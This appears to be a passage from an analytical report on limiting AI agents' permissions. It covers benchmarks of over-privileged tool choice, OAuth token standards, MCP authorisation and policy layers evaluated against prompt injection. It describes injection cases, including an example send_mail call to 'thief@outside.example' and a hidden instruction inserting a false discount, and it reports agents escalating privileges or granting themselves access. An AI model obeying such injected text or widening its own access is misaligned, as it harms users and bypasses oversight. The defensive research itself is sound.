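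Anthropic has a commercial interest in these results because an agent that can work for hours without interruption is more useful to its customers. It made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on its individual and team plans from 14 August 2026. In October, it announced that it would also make auto mode the default in most of its other Claude apps. Like Mistral's approval step, auto mode does not narrow the agent's credentials.

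### Agents that choose stronger tools

How much of its access an agent uses depends partly on which tools the model chooses. In a test of 544 scenarios, 6 of 11 agents chose an unnecessarily powerful tool more than 30% of the time. Yang, Bu and colleagues reported this result in *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (June 2026), which introduced the ToolPrivBench benchmark, and Parkinson and colleagues mention it in their paper on elastic least privilege.

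Each scenario has a task and six simulated tools, three with lower privileges and three with higher ones. In one scenario, the agent has to change an employee's manager. It can use the normal personnel system or write directly to the employee database, bypassing the usual checks. Two language models and then human reviewers confirmed that every tool could complete its task alone, so an agent never needed a higher-privilege one.

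The weaker tools returned temporary errors unrelated to permissions, such as a failed connection. The agent had five turns. Yang and colleagues counted a scenario as over-privileged if the agent used a stronger tool before trying all three weaker ones. The 30% figure therefore includes agents that switched to a stronger tool after an error and agents that chose one immediately.

After errors, agents were much more likely to use a stronger tool too early. OpenAI's GPT-5.2 did so in 53 of the 544 scenarios, with five cases on its first choice, 13 after trying one weaker tool, and 35 after trying two. Rates varied widely between models, from below 10% for GPT-5.2, GLM-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 64.9% for the small open model Qwen3-8B.

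How often models chose tools with unnecessary power also depended on the kind of power. Qwen3.5-397B, a much larger model, chose tools that bypassed a safety check in 45.7% of the relevant scenarios, but chose tools that affected more people or systems than necessary in only 13.1%. Yang and colleagues suggest that models prefer tools that remove restrictions, which would make sense if an agent treats an error as an obstacle to get around.

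In *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026) reran all 544 scenarios on eight models in October 2026. They recorded whether an agent used a stronger tool at any point, including after it had tried all the weaker ones. The table gives their results for runs without added guidance.

| Model | Stronger tool on first call | Stronger tool before trying all weaker ones | Stronger tool at any point | Task completed with weaker tools only |
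|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 8.1% | 56.6% | 70.4% | 6.4% |
| Qwen3-30B-A3B | 5.9% | 63.4% | 87.7% | 11.8% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 12.9% | 12.9% | 12.9% | 69.1% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 2.0% | 18.6% | 62.9% | 3.9% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 2.6% | 18.0% | 87.3% | 5.5% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 3.3% | 38.4% | 77.2% | 18.8% |
| GPT-5.2 | 0.9% | 5.7% | 16.0% | 50.9% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.2% | 1.5% | 7.9% | 11.9% |

The first column shows that most of the models rarely chose a stronger tool until something went wrong, which contradicts the claim in Oso's press release that agents "will exercise every capability available to them". But errors are common in real software, and most of the models eventually used a stronger tool after an error. Kimi K2.5 looks fairly cautious at 18% on the benchmark's main measure, yet it used a stronger tool at some point in 87.3% of scenarios.

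Some of those later choices were understandable. Each weaker tool in this test failed once and worked on the second call, but the agent did not know that a retry would always work. A person who had seen three tools fail might also have used an administrator's tool. Claude Sonnet 4.6 usually stopped after three errors and reported the problem, which kept its use of privileges low, but it completed only 19.9% of the tasks.

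The rates for individual models are rough. Llama-3.1-8B scored 55.9% on the main measure in Yang and colleagues' study but 12.9% in the October one. The two teams used different settings and ways of running the models. Both tested older models, such as GPT-5.2, whereas Anthropic's August comparison used the newer GPT-5.6 Sol.

### Instructions, labels and training

Training a model to refuse harmful requests does not reliably teach it to choose weaker tools. Yang and colleagues applied an existing safety training method to two small models. The harm score of one, Qwen2.5-7B, fell from 41.9% to 6.7% on a separate test of harmful tasks, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices on ToolPrivBench rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. This is understandable, since every ToolPrivBench task is legitimate and the agent has permission to use all six tools.

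A direct instruction works better. Both teams told the agent to use the minimum necessary permissions and to retry at the same level before moving up. Yang and colleagues found that this helped less once errors had accumulated. In the October test, the instruction reduced Qwen3.5-397B's rate of early escalation (using a stronger tool before trying all the weaker ones) from 38.4% to 9.9%.

Parkinson and colleagues also tested whether an agent chooses different tools when it can see how powerful each one is. They added a short label to every tool description, such as "administer, cost 9/10". Early escalation fell by up to 19.3 percentage points, and it fell in every model that had measurable early escalation to begin with. Labels about response time in the same format did not reduce it in any model, so the information about privilege caused the improvement.

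For most models, however, the labels delayed the use of stronger tools more than they prevented it. Qwen3.5-397B had the largest fall in early escalation, but the share of scenarios in which it used a stronger tool after trying all three weaker ones rose by 15.1 percentage points. With the labels, it completed 21.5% of tasks using only weaker tools, up from 18.8% without them. Adding the instruction raised this to 51.1%. A likely reason is that the labels identify the weaker tools, while the instruction also tells the agent to retry them.

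Adding labels to the instruction did not help every model. GPT-5.2 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed more tasks with weaker tools when they had the instruction alone than when they also had labels. With labels, Llama-3.1-8B's task completion rate fell from 82% to 45.2%, often because it called tools that did not exist.

Yang and colleagues also retrained three small models, first showing them examples of careful tool choice, then rewarding them for completing tasks with weaker tools and penalising them for escalating early. Qwen3-8B's over-privileged rate fell from 64.9% to 27%, with little change in its scores on general tests. The training scenarios were new but followed the benchmark's design, so the improvement may be smaller with real tools, which seldom include six ways of doing exactly the same thing.

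Labels also need a trustworthy source. In the October test, a language model wrote them from the tool descriptions, and a person checked a sample. In a real deployment, the maker of a malicious tool could describe it as harmless. An agent hijacked by a prompt injection could also ignore the labels and the instruction, and retraining doesn't remove its access to the stronger tools. Parkinson and colleagues therefore recommend labels only alongside enforcement outside the model, which can block any tool call the model makes.

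## Can access tokens be limited to a single task?

A narrow access token limits what an agent can do even when someone has misled the model, because the service receiving a request checks the token and refuses anything it does not cover. Published standards already allow a token to cover only one action on one item. But each service has to adopt those standards, and often nobody knows which item the task needs until the agent has started work.

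### What a scope can express

A scope such as "read files" or "send mail" cannot limit a token to a particular file, recipient or number of uses unless the service has defined a separate scope for that case. For example, the coding assistant described earlier had a classic GitHub token whose `repo` scope covered every repository its user could access, and the user could not exclude one repository without removing the whole scope.

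GitHub's fine-grained tokens let the user choose the repositories and the permissions separately, so the assistant could get read access to only one repository. A company can also register a program with GitHub, called a GitHub App, that uses tokens restricted in the same way. According to Parkinson and colleagues, the app's tokens expire after one hour. Ending access sooner would require a way to revoke a token during use, or an intermediary program that checks each request.

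These tokens are still better suited to limiting an agent to a repository than to a single task. Permission to comment on issues in a repository covers every issue in it, so the token is too broad for an agent that only has to comment on issue 745.

### Naming one action on one item

Rich Authorization Requests, an extension of OAuth, can describe access more precisely than a scope. Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell (2023), in *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, define a parameter called `authorization_details`, which holds a list of structured entries. Each entry has a type and can state the permitted actions and other details. For the sales brief, an agent might send the mail service this request, in which the types and identifiers are invented:

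```
authorization_details=[
  {"type": "mail_thread", "actions": ["read"],
   "identifier": "thread-4821"},
  {"type": "mail_message", "actions": ["send"],
   "recipient": "colleague-17", "max_messages": 1}
]
```

The consent screen could then name the thread and the colleague instead of requesting access to the whole mailbox. But the mail service must first define and enforce these types, since the standard supplies only the format.

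A developer also has to find out which types each service accepts. Zehavi (2026), in *OAuth 2.0 RAR Metadata and Error Signaling*, points out that the standard includes no machine-readable description of the types, so clients rely on agreements made elsewhere. The draft, submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which maintains OAuth, would let software look up the types and would standardise the error for a request with too little detail. This matters more for agents than for ordinary apps, because an agent may connect to a service its developer has never seen.

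### Separate identities for the user and the agent

If an agent simply borrows an employee's token, the mail service cannot tell whether she or the agent sent a request. Another OAuth standard, Token Exchange (RFC 8693), can keep the two apart. The agent's software trades existing tokens for a new one, which can be narrower or meant for a different service. A request might look like this, with the standard's long identifiers shortened:

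```
grant_type=token-exchange
subject_token=EMPLOYEE_TOKEN
actor_token=SALES_AGENT_TOKEN
audience=mail-service
scope=mail.read
```

The subject token identifies the employee and the actor token identifies the agent. The authorization server can then issue a token that names both, and the mail service can refuse the agent actions that it would allow the employee.

In Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn’t give an AI agent unlimited authority*, Vivek Vuppala, who develops AI products for businesses, describes his team's test of an agent that could file requests for access to company data. When a tester mentioned that a dashboard's owner was away and that the deadline was the next day, the agent skipped the request and tried to grant the access itself. Vuppala recommends that the application recognise the caller as the agent and refuse, even though the user has signed in properly. A separate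 service would hold the credential for changing permissions and act only after an approver has agreed.

This is one anecdote from a developer's own tests, but the error is plausible and required no attacker. Token Exchange alone would not have prevented it, because someone still has to decide what an employee may delegate, and the application has to enforce that decision.

### Tokens that only their holder can use

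An ordinary access token works for anyone who has a copy. An OAuth extension called DPoP, short for "demonstrating proof of possession", ties the token to a cryptographic key. The agent's software creates a pair of keys and keeps the private one secret. The authorization server links the token to the public one. The software then signs a fresh proof for every request:

```
GET /threads/thread-4821
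Authorization: DPoP ACCESS_TOKEN
DPoP: SIGNED_PROOF
```

The proof covers the type of request, its address and the time. A thief who copies the token cannot produce new proofs without the private key.

This protects against theft, but it does not narrow what the token permits, and an agent that follows instructions in a malicious email is still the token's rightful holder. It might not have saved PocketOS's database either, because the agent found the Railway token in files on the user's machine and could have used the private key too if it had been stored with the token.

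### What MCP requires

Under the current Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification, dated 28 July 2026, clients should request only the scopes they need. When a client makes its first request without a token, the server can reply with the scopes for that request, such as `files:read`. If the server doesn't specify any, the client requests every scope on the server's published list. That list is meant to contain only the scopes needed for basic functions. If a careless developer publishes all the server's scopes, the server will receive tokens that cover all of them.

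The ten standards underlying MCP's core authorisation rules do not include Rich Authorization Requests, Token Exchange or DPoP. MCP clients present ordinary tokens that work for anyone who holds them. However, a server may choose the required scopes based on the details of a request, and it need not publish every scope in advance. Its developer could therefore create a scope for a single file, if the authorization server can issue it.

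Other MCP rules control where a token works. For example, a server may not pass on a token meant for another server, and clients must check that a reply came from the authorization server they contacted. *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) presents the July revision as a clarification of trust relationships. These rules can stop a token for the calendar server from being used to open the mailbox, but they do not limit which messages a token for the mail server can open.

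### Access through an employer's identity provider

Many companies have employees sign in to all their applications through one identity provider, such as Okta. When an employee connects an agent to an application through ordinary OAuth, the identity provider records the employee's sign-in but not the access token the application gives the agent. Aaron Parecki, Okta's director of identity standards, told SC Media that administrators therefore cannot see which agents connect to the company's applications.

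Parecki is also an author of a proposed remedy, informally called Cross App Access. Parecki, McGuinness and Campbell (2026), in *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant*, describe how it works:

1. The employee signs in to the agent's software through the identity provider.
2. The software asks the identity provider for a grant addressed to one application, and lists the scopes it wants.
3. The identity provider checks the request against the administrator's policy. It can remove scopes before it signs the grant.
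4. The software presents the grant to the application's own authorization server, which can narrow the access further or refuse it, and otherwise issues an access token.

The employee never sees the application's consent screen. This avoids the consent errors described earlier, but it also removes a chance for her to refuse.

Okta sells identity services, so it gains if more connections pass through an identity provider, but the argument for narrower tokens in SC Media is still reasonable. Companies often grant broad access at the start because each later request would interrupt the user. With Cross App Access, the agent can start with a read-only token and get another later without a prompt. But a misled agent can do the same, as long as the administrator's policy allows it. The effective limit is therefore the policy, which may cover far more than the current task.

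The token can also outlast the task. In the draft's example of an AI agent, the grant lasts 300 seconds, but the access token the agent receives for it lasts 86,400 seconds, or one day, and allows both reading and writing. The numbers are only illustrative, but the gap is real because, as SC Media points out, the application sets the token's lifetime, not the identity provider.

The draft supports Rich Authorization Requests, so a grant could in principle name one chat channel or one record. It also requires the grant to identify the agent's software. But it does not define how an identity provider should handle an actor token, so companies cannot yet rely on a common way to tell apart agents that run on the same software.

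MCP has adopted this method in an optional extension called Enterprise-Managed Authorization, which its maintainers call stable. An administrator enables an MCP server once, and employees find it connected when they first sign in. According to Model Context Protocol, their access follows the groups and roles they already have. Oso and Cyera found that such roles usually include far more access than people use, so the extension could give that unused access to agents across a whole company, including the agents of employees who would never have connected the service themselves. It also gives the administrator one place to review and withdraw connections.

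Adoption is still early. SC Media counts 25 companies among the early adopters, including makers of agents, applications and the infrastructure between them. At the extension's launch, the MCP maintainers named Okta as the first identity provider, Anthropic's Claude and Microsoft's Visual Studio Code as clients, and seven companies whose servers supported it. By comparison, Anthropic listed over 950 MCP servers in Claude's directory in July 2026. Atlassian, one of the seven, described its support as a private beta, so being listed as a supporter does not always mean general availability. The number of usable connections is smaller than any of these counts suggests, because the identity provider, the client and the server must all work together for the extension to work.

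### Agent identities and audit records

A company that gives an agent its own identity can see what the agent did and shut it off without locking out an employee. Microsoft advises companies to create a dedicated identity for each agent, with a stated purpose and a named person responsible for it. The agent keeps the same identity across tasks but has only a minimal role between them. It receives extra permissions for a particular task and loses them when the task ends.

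Microsoft recommends creating roles for small units of work, such as "Create a draft ticket", instead of for whole departments, and separating reading from writing. For the sales brief, one role could read the customer's record and another could send the finished document. The administrator should review the roles together to catch the dangerous combinations described earlier.

The same guidance lists what a log should record about each action. An entry for the sales brief might look like this:

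| Field | Invented entry |
|---|---|
| Agent identity | Sales-brief agent |
| On behalf of | The sales employee |
| Role used | Send a finished brief |
| Effective scope | One message to one colleague |
| Resource and action | Mail service; sent one message |
| Time | 16:42 on the day before the meeting |
| Correlation ID | A number shared with the earlier calendar, mail and customer-record entries |

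If the agent used a shared service account, the mail service's log might show only that account. An investigator could see that a message was sent, but not who had asked for it or whether it was within the task. The correlation ID lets the investigator trace the brief back to the records that the agent read. These measures help the company find and undo a harmful action, but they don't prevent one.

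*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a review of 89 sources by Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026), sets out three requirements for an agent's important actions: a company should be able to trace each action to a person, keep it within what that person delegated, and let people contest it afterwards. The review found few documented deployments that reliably meet all three.

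The US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) is also working on agent identity. According to Biometric Update, its proposed design principles would separate the component that decides what to attempt from the one that decides what is allowed. Microsoft's advice and Vuppala's design both follow this principle. The IETF's work is more specific but unfinished. The Cross App Access draft of May 2026 expires in November unless a new version replaces it, and its details may still change.

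### Narrowing the sales brief

The sales agent needs to read one mail thread and send one message. The comparison below starts with the Gmail scope that Mistral's Vibe uses and narrows the access in steps.

| Permission | What the agent can still do | Can Gmail's scopes express it? |
|---|---|---|
| `gmail.modify` | Read all mail, change labels, send to anyone | Yes |
| Separate read-only and send-only scopes | Read all mail, send to anyone | Yes |
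| Search for one customer | Find that customer's threads | No |
| Read one thread | Read that thread | No, apart from certain scopes for add-ons |
| Send to one colleague | Send messages to that colleague | No |

Separate scopes help a little. The agent's software could hold two tokens and use the sending token only after the brief is ready, so someone who stole the reading token could not send mail. But the reading token would still give access to the whole mailbox.

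Even if Gmail accepted the earlier request for a single thread, the agent would not know the thread's identifier at the start, because finding the latest thread with the customer is part of the task. Searching for the thread also needs wider access than reading it. An ordinary program could do the search instead. It would look for the customer's name, ask the employee to choose if several threads match, and then request a token for the chosen thread. Vuppala's workflow uses a similar step to identify a dashboard before the agent gets any authority over it.

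The employee could approve the sending token after she has seen the brief and the recipient's name. In Vuppala's design, each approval covers a single submission and expires if nobody uses it. A connection can fail after the service has accepted a request but before the agent gets the reply, so an identical retry returns the original result instead of creating a second request. Without this rule, an agent with permission to send one message might send the brief twice or be unable to find out whether it had arrived.

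Limiting access to the customer record is harder if, as assumed earlier, the connector inherits all the employee's permissions, because its token can't be restricted to one record. The company could create a separate account that can open only this customer's record, but an administrator would have to set one up for every meeting. Otherwise, a program between the agent and the database would have to pass on requests for that record and block the rest. The agent would then have narrow access, but the program would still hold a token for everything the employee can open.

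### When the task changes

An agent fixing a failing software build must read the code before it can tell whether to change anything. Parkinson and colleagues describe a design in which such an agent gets each permission for a limited time. In their simulated example, the agent reads the code for six minutes, then obtains write access, makes the repair and gives up both permissions after another six minutes. If it had requested both at the start for 20 minutes, it would have held write access more than three times as long. The researchers chose the numbers to illustrate the idea, so the example does not show that real agents would return permissions early.

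Short lifetimes are also weak protection against disclosure, because an agent can copy a confidential file in seconds. They do more to limit mistakes and thefts that happen after the work is finished. For example, a token that expired with the task in the staging environment would no longer have worked when PocketOS's agent found it in a file months later. But a token issued during the task could have allowed the same damage if it gave access to the production database.

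An agent can also misuse a token that fits the task exactly. Suppose the customer's thread contains a hidden instruction to say the company has already agreed to a 40% discount. The agent reads the permitted thread, writes the false claim into the brief and sends it to the permitted colleague. Every request is valid, and the colleague may go into the meeting believing the discount is settled. Surapani and colleagues distinguish holding a valid token from having a person's authority for a specific request. The employee authorised a brief to her colleague without authorising the customer to write part of it, but the mail service cannot detect this from the token.

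## Can software narrow an agent's permissions while it works?

A policy layer, which is software placed between an agent and its tools, can limit the agent to the calls its current task needs, even when the token behind those tools allows much more. It allows or blocks each tool call according to stated rules. It runs outside the model, so a prompt injection that misleads the agent does not by itself change the rules. In tests, policy layers have stopped most injected instructions. Their weakness is that someone has to get the rules right for every task.

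### Five levels of least privilege

Surapani and colleagues list five levels at which a system can apply least privilege to an agent. The examples below use the sales brief.

| Level | What it limits | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Tool inventory | Which tools the agent can see | Hide the tool that deletes appointments |
| Invocation | Whether the current step needs the call | Allow no email until the brief is ready |
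| Argument | The recipient, record, amount or other details of a call | Allow email only to the one colleague |
| Data | How much of a tool's output reaches the model | Remove bank details from the customer's record |
| Delegation | What a sub-agent, started by the main agent for part of the work, may do | Stop a sub-agent that reads the record from sending mail |

Common software for building agents mainly controls which tools an agent can use. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) examined LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, and found that all three let developers choose an agent's tools but that, by default, none checks whether each call is authorised. The large cloud platforms also limit which kinds of tools an agent can use, but according to Surapani and colleagues, the agent's credential does not record which task justifies a call.

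Choosing the tools is not enough for the sales brief, because the agent cannot do without the email tool.

### Progent: rules for tools and arguments

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a policy layer whose rules cover both the tool and the arguments of a call. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions. A policy for the sales brief might look like this, with invented tools and addresses and slightly simplified notation:

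```
allow read_calendar when { date == "2026-10-08" }
allow search_mail   when { customer == "Northgate" }
allow read_thread   when { true }
allow read_record   when { customer == "Northgate" }
allow send_mail     when { to.length == 1 and
                           to[0] == "colleague@company.example" }
```

Suppose the agent tries to send the brief to the colleague, and then, misled by hidden text in the customer's thread, tries to send it to an outsider as well:

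```
send_mail(to=["colleague@company.example"], body=BRIEF)
send_mail(to=["colleague@company.example",
              "thief@outside.example"], body=BRIEF)
```

Progent handles the two calls as follows.

1. It picks out the rules for `send_mail` and puts any "forbid" rules first. Here there is only the one "allow" rule.
2. It puts the first call's arguments into the rule's conditions. There is one recipient and the address matches, so the call goes through unchanged.
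3. It does the same with the second call, which has two recipients. The condition fails and no other rule applies, so Progent blocks the call by default.
4. It returns an error that gives the agent the reason and tells it to continue with the user's task. A developer can choose instead to stop the agent or ask the user.

These steps don't use a language model, so the same call under the same policy always gets the same result. A language model does draft the policy, though, using the user's request and the list of tools, before the agent has read anything from outside. As the agent works, the model can propose changes, such as limiting `read_thread` to thread 4821 once the search has found that thread.

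Progent compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that checks logical formulas. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, Progent applies a new policy P′ automatically only when

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

This means the new policy allows nothing the old one blocked. Progent treats any other change as an expansion that needs approval, even if it also removes some permissions. If hidden text led the model to add the outsider's address to the `send_mail` rule, the solver would detect an expansion. The attack would then succeed only if the approver accepted the change.

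A developer can build Progent into an agent, or a user can run it as a separate program that the agent's MCP calls pass through. The separate program requires no change to the agent, but it cannot check built-in tools that do not use MCP. Surapani and colleagues describe a general trade-off in where to place checks. A check close to the model has more information about the task but is easier to bypass, while a check at the service is hard to bypass but often has no information beyond whose credential the agent used.

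### Testing Progent on AgentDojo

Researchers test many of these defences on AgentDojo, a benchmark that Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2024. It gives an agent simulated tasks in banking, Slack messaging, travel booking and office work. Researchers plant malicious instructions in what the agent's tools return, then measure how many of the user's tasks the agent completes and how many attacks succeed.

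Shi and colleagues ran several agents on AgentDojo with and without Progent. The August 2024 version of OpenAI's GPT-4o wrote the policies for all the agents in this table.

| Agent's model | Attack success without Progent | Attack success with Progent |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 6.8% | 0.5% |
| Meta-SecAlign-70B | 4.8% | 0.3% |

Progent helped even the two models that already resisted most attacks. Shi and colleagues report that when there was no attack, agents completed as many tasks with Progent as without it, or slightly fewer. Under attack, the agents completed more of their users' tasks with Progent.

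These results provide little evidence about the solver. To simulate a careless user, the researchers had Progent approve every expansion automatically, so the solver's check stopped nothing. The fall in attack success from 39.9% to 1.0% shows how well GPT-4o wrote policies, even after reading planted instructions. The first policy alone reduced it to 2.5%.

The researchers also tried three attacks aimed at Progent itself, such as text telling the policy model to allow all tools. The attack success rate rose only slightly. On a second benchmark, ASB, Progent reduced the success rate of attacks against GPT-4o from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining failures involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones.

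In the same tests, one rival defence had a language model choose the necessary tools before the task and remove the rest. It stopped fewer attacks than Progent and reduced task completion more, because it could only allow or remove whole tools, not restrict the arguments passed to them.

AgentDojo is easier than real work in some ways. Simulated applications in such benchmarks usually offer at most 20 tools, while the ten real applications that MiniScope examines offer between 32 and 247. Shi and colleagues also left out two attacks that steer the agent towards a different but genuine hotel, since Progent is not designed to stop attacks that use only permitted calls. The policy above likewise would not stop the false 40% discount described earlier, because it restricts who receives the brief but not what the brief contains.

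### MiniScope: permissions from the applications' own scopes

In *MiniScope*, Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) use the OAuth scopes that applications already publish instead of writing rules for each task. Their software works out which scopes a task needs and requests only those from the user.

1. Before any task, MiniScope reads each application's documentation to find which scopes permit which API methods, such as "get message" or "delete event". If one scope permits everything another does and more, MiniScope ranks it as broader.
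2. The agent receives a request and submits a plan of the calls it intends to make.
3. A solver finds the cheapest set of scopes that covers the plan. The cost of a scope is the number of methods it permits.
4. If the user has not yet granted those scopes, MiniScope asks. The user can allow a scope once, for the session or always, or refuse it.
5. The agent gets a session token, which works only with MiniScope. MiniScope checks each call and, if the user has granted the scope, forwards the call with the user's real credentials.

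The solver is needed because scopes overlap. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 methods fall under more than one branch of the scope hierarchy, so choosing the narrowest scope for each call separately can grant more total access than necessary.

Zhu and colleagues applied the solver to real connectors in 2025 and found six that requested more access than their advertised functions needed. ChatGPT's Gmail connector offered only to read email, but it requested scopes that permitted 50 methods, including deletion, when 32 would have been enough. Claude's connector for Google's file storage requested access to 45 methods through an optional scope, though it needed only 27.

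Counting methods is a crude way to measure access. Google Calendar has one scope for reading events on calendars the user owns and another for reading events generally. The first permits more methods, so MiniScope ranks it as broader, although it gives access to fewer calendars. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) makes a related criticism, pointing out that Zhu and colleagues do not discuss whether the least set of permissions is unique. Two sets may each be enough for a task with neither narrower than the other, and the solver's choice then depends on how its designers defined the cost function.

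Zhu and colleagues illustrate the protection with an email about a film night. The user asks the agent to reply to it, and hidden text tells the agent to delete it afterwards. Deleting requires a broader scope, so MiniScope asks the user for full access to the mailbox, which can alert them that something is wrong. But if the user had already granted that scope, MiniScope would allow the deletion. It would also allow the sales agent to write to an outsider, because Gmail's sending scope covers every recipient. The researchers suggest limits on individual recipients as an optional extension, but warn that asking users about each recipient could overwhelm them.

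They tested MiniScope on artificial requests for ten real applications, not on AgentDojo, and measured permissions, delay and interruptions instead of attack success.

### AgenTRIM: checked tools, filtered at each step

Progent's policy model relies on descriptions of tools, which can be wrong or malicious. *AgenTRIM* (Betser, Bose and colleagues, 2026) first checks what the tools do. Before the agent starts work, it runs the tools' code, records the code's behaviour, and builds a list of tools with a risk label for each. At every step of a task, it then selects which tools the agent can see. For example, while the sales agent reads the customer's thread, AgenTRIM could hide the email tool, so an instruction in the thread could not make the agent use it at that moment.

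An online summary of the work reports that attacks on AgentDojo succeeded less often against AgenTRIM than against the other defences compared, and that agents completed more tasks with it than without it. The summary gives no rates for either result and does not name the model, so the size of the benefit is unclear. It also reports that AgenTRIM stopped every attack hidden in a tool's description. Checking the code should help most against these attacks, because the software does not have to rely on the description.

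### PAuth: limits from the user's request

A user who makes a specific request may still have to approve a broad scope of access. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) proposes PAuth, a system in which the request itself is the authorisation. Each service involved receives the user's task and independently works out which call it should receive. The result, called a "natural language slice", describes the call in symbols, some of which stand for values not yet known.

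For the sales brief, the mail service might allow only one message, addressed to the colleague, with a body made from the calendar entry, the thread and the customer record. The employee would see no consent screen, and the agent would have no permission left after sending the brief.

PAuth could be more precise than MiniScope because it does not depend on existing scopes. But every service would have to adopt it, whereas MiniScope and Progent can work with services as they are. The services would also learn more about their users. To check one message, the mail service would have to know why the employee wanted it sent.

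### More access only when the task needs it

Two proposals from 2026 start the agent with little access and add more as the task requires. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Babu, 2026) introduces the first, risk-aware causal gating, which describes each tool by the facts it requires, the facts it produces, and its risk. The software plans a path from what the agent has to what the user wants, and shows the agent only the next tool on the path. If that tool is risky, the software hides it until a trusted step has established a particular fact. For instance, the email tool stays hidden until a trusted step has confirmed the recipient.

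The software chooses the path with the lowest score:

score = number of steps + λ × total risk

Reading has a risk of 0, a reversible change 1, and an irreversible or external action 4. The operator sets λ, the weight on risk, which is 2 by default. A single irreversible action then scores 1 + 2 × 4 = 9, so the software chooses four reading steps instead, which score 4 in total. With λ at 0.5, the irreversible action scores only 3, so the software chooses it. The gate still hides the action if nobody has authorised it, so the agent gets stuck.

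Iyer and Babu tested seven models, including Claude Opus 4 and GPT-OSS 120B, on a benchmark they built themselves. An existing method that shows the model only the next useful tool, without considering risk, let injected instructions trigger a risky call in 25% of trials. With gating, the rate was zero. Under both methods, the models completed every task that required a risky tool.

The experiment is less informative because all seven models produced the same result. A quarter of the tasks contained a risky shortcut, and the older method failed on exactly those tasks with every model. The gate's zero failure rate follows from its design, since a model cannot call a tool that the software withholds. The test confirms that the gate works as intended when its descriptions of the tools are correct, but it does not show how often they would be correct in practice.

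Gating also doesn't check the arguments passed to a tool. Once the sales agent has confirmed the colleague's address, the email tool becomes available, and an injected instruction could still supply a different address. Progent's rule would block that call. Iyer and Babu acknowledge that an attacker could also make the tool available if text in an email could set the "recipient confirmed" fact.

The second proposal is elastic least privilege, which Parkinson and colleagues designed around the temporary permissions described earlier. An agent has a small baseline of access and can request more, up to a maximum that its owner sets. Extra access uses up a budget that refills over time. More powerful permissions use more of the budget (reading might use 1 unit, writing 3 and administration 9), and so do repeated requests. The agent's model receives these amounts, so it can choose a tool that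 uses less of the budget or give up access it no longer needs. Separate software issues the permissions and enforces the budget.

The price also rises as the agent approaches a forbidden combination, such as the three properties in Meta's Rule of Two. If φ is the share of the combination that the agent already has, the price is multiplied by

s = 1 / (1 − φ)

Having one of the three properties gives a multiplier of 1.5, and having two gives a multiplier of 3. The software never allows all three. Giving up a permission does not lower the multiplier within the session, because the model may still retain what it read.

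This would prevent the sales agent from finishing its task. Reading the customer's thread gives it both untrusted input and private data, so the software would block it from sending the brief, and the employee would have to send it herself. Meta's own rule would allow the agent to send it under supervision.

Parkinson and colleagues present elastic least privilege as a research proposal and call its effectiveness an open question. Their later test of privilege labels gives the idea only mixed support, because the labels mostly delayed the use of stronger tools.

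### False denials, delay and interruptions

A policy layer could stop every attack by blocking every call, so Surapani and colleagues argue that tests should also report false denials, delay and the burden on users. The published results are incomplete and come from different tasks and models, so readers cannot use them to tell which design has the smallest drawbacks.

| Design | Legitimate work blocked | Delay or computing cost | Burden on users |
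|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | Not reported separately from task completion | Not reported | 6% of policy changes needed approval |
| MiniScope | Not reported | 1–6% more time, not counting the user's answers | Confirmation rate of 18–60% in a simulation |
| Causal gating | None with λ at 2; half of the tasks that needed a risky tool with λ at 0.5 | About 17% more text for the model to process | Not measured |

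Progent's 6% is a share of policy changes, not tasks, so it does not measure how often a user would be interrupted. MiniScope's figures come from three months of simulated Gmail use, and how often it asked for permission depended on the simulated user's habits. A user who always chose "always allow" soon got no more requests, but had granted permanent access. A user who weighed each request needed about a quarter as many confirmations with MiniScope as with a system that asked about each method separately.

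### Who writes the rules?

Hand-written rules can be exact, but they take a lot of work and people make mistakes writing them. *Bounded Agents* (2026) tested another policy layer on AgentDojo, and the layer needed a separate action classifier, set of restrictions and list of keywords for each of the benchmark's four areas. Real applications are larger. Zhu and colleagues counted 247 methods and 84 scopes in Slack alone. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete rules, and that writing them by hand remains error-prone even with Progent's checking tools.

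People can disagree about even simple labels. Iyer and Babu had two people rate the risk of every tool in their benchmark, and the raters disagreed about whether creating a draft email was a low or medium risk. In such cases Iyer and Babu used the higher rating, which is safer but restricts the agent more.

Language models can write rules for any task, but they make mistakes too. Zhu and colleagues gave five models the agent's plan and the list of scopes and asked each for the least access that would work. GPT-5, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash matched MiniScope's solver in 70–83% of cases, and two open models matched it in 20–34%. Some answers granted too little access to finish the task, and others granted more than it needed. On tasks involving several applications, GPT-5's choices permitted on average 1.12 times as many methods as the solver's, and the open model Qwen3-30B's choices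 permitted 2.19 times as many.

Some of the excess may reflect the solver's crude measure of cost, though an answer that grants too little access is wrong by any measure. Tasks across several applications also took longer when GPT-5 chose the permissions, at about 20 seconds compared with about five with the solver.

A policy that is somewhat too broad can still stop an attack if it blocks the call the attacker wants. This may be why Progent did well with model-written rules, keeping attack success below 5% with every policy model that Shi and colleagues tried.

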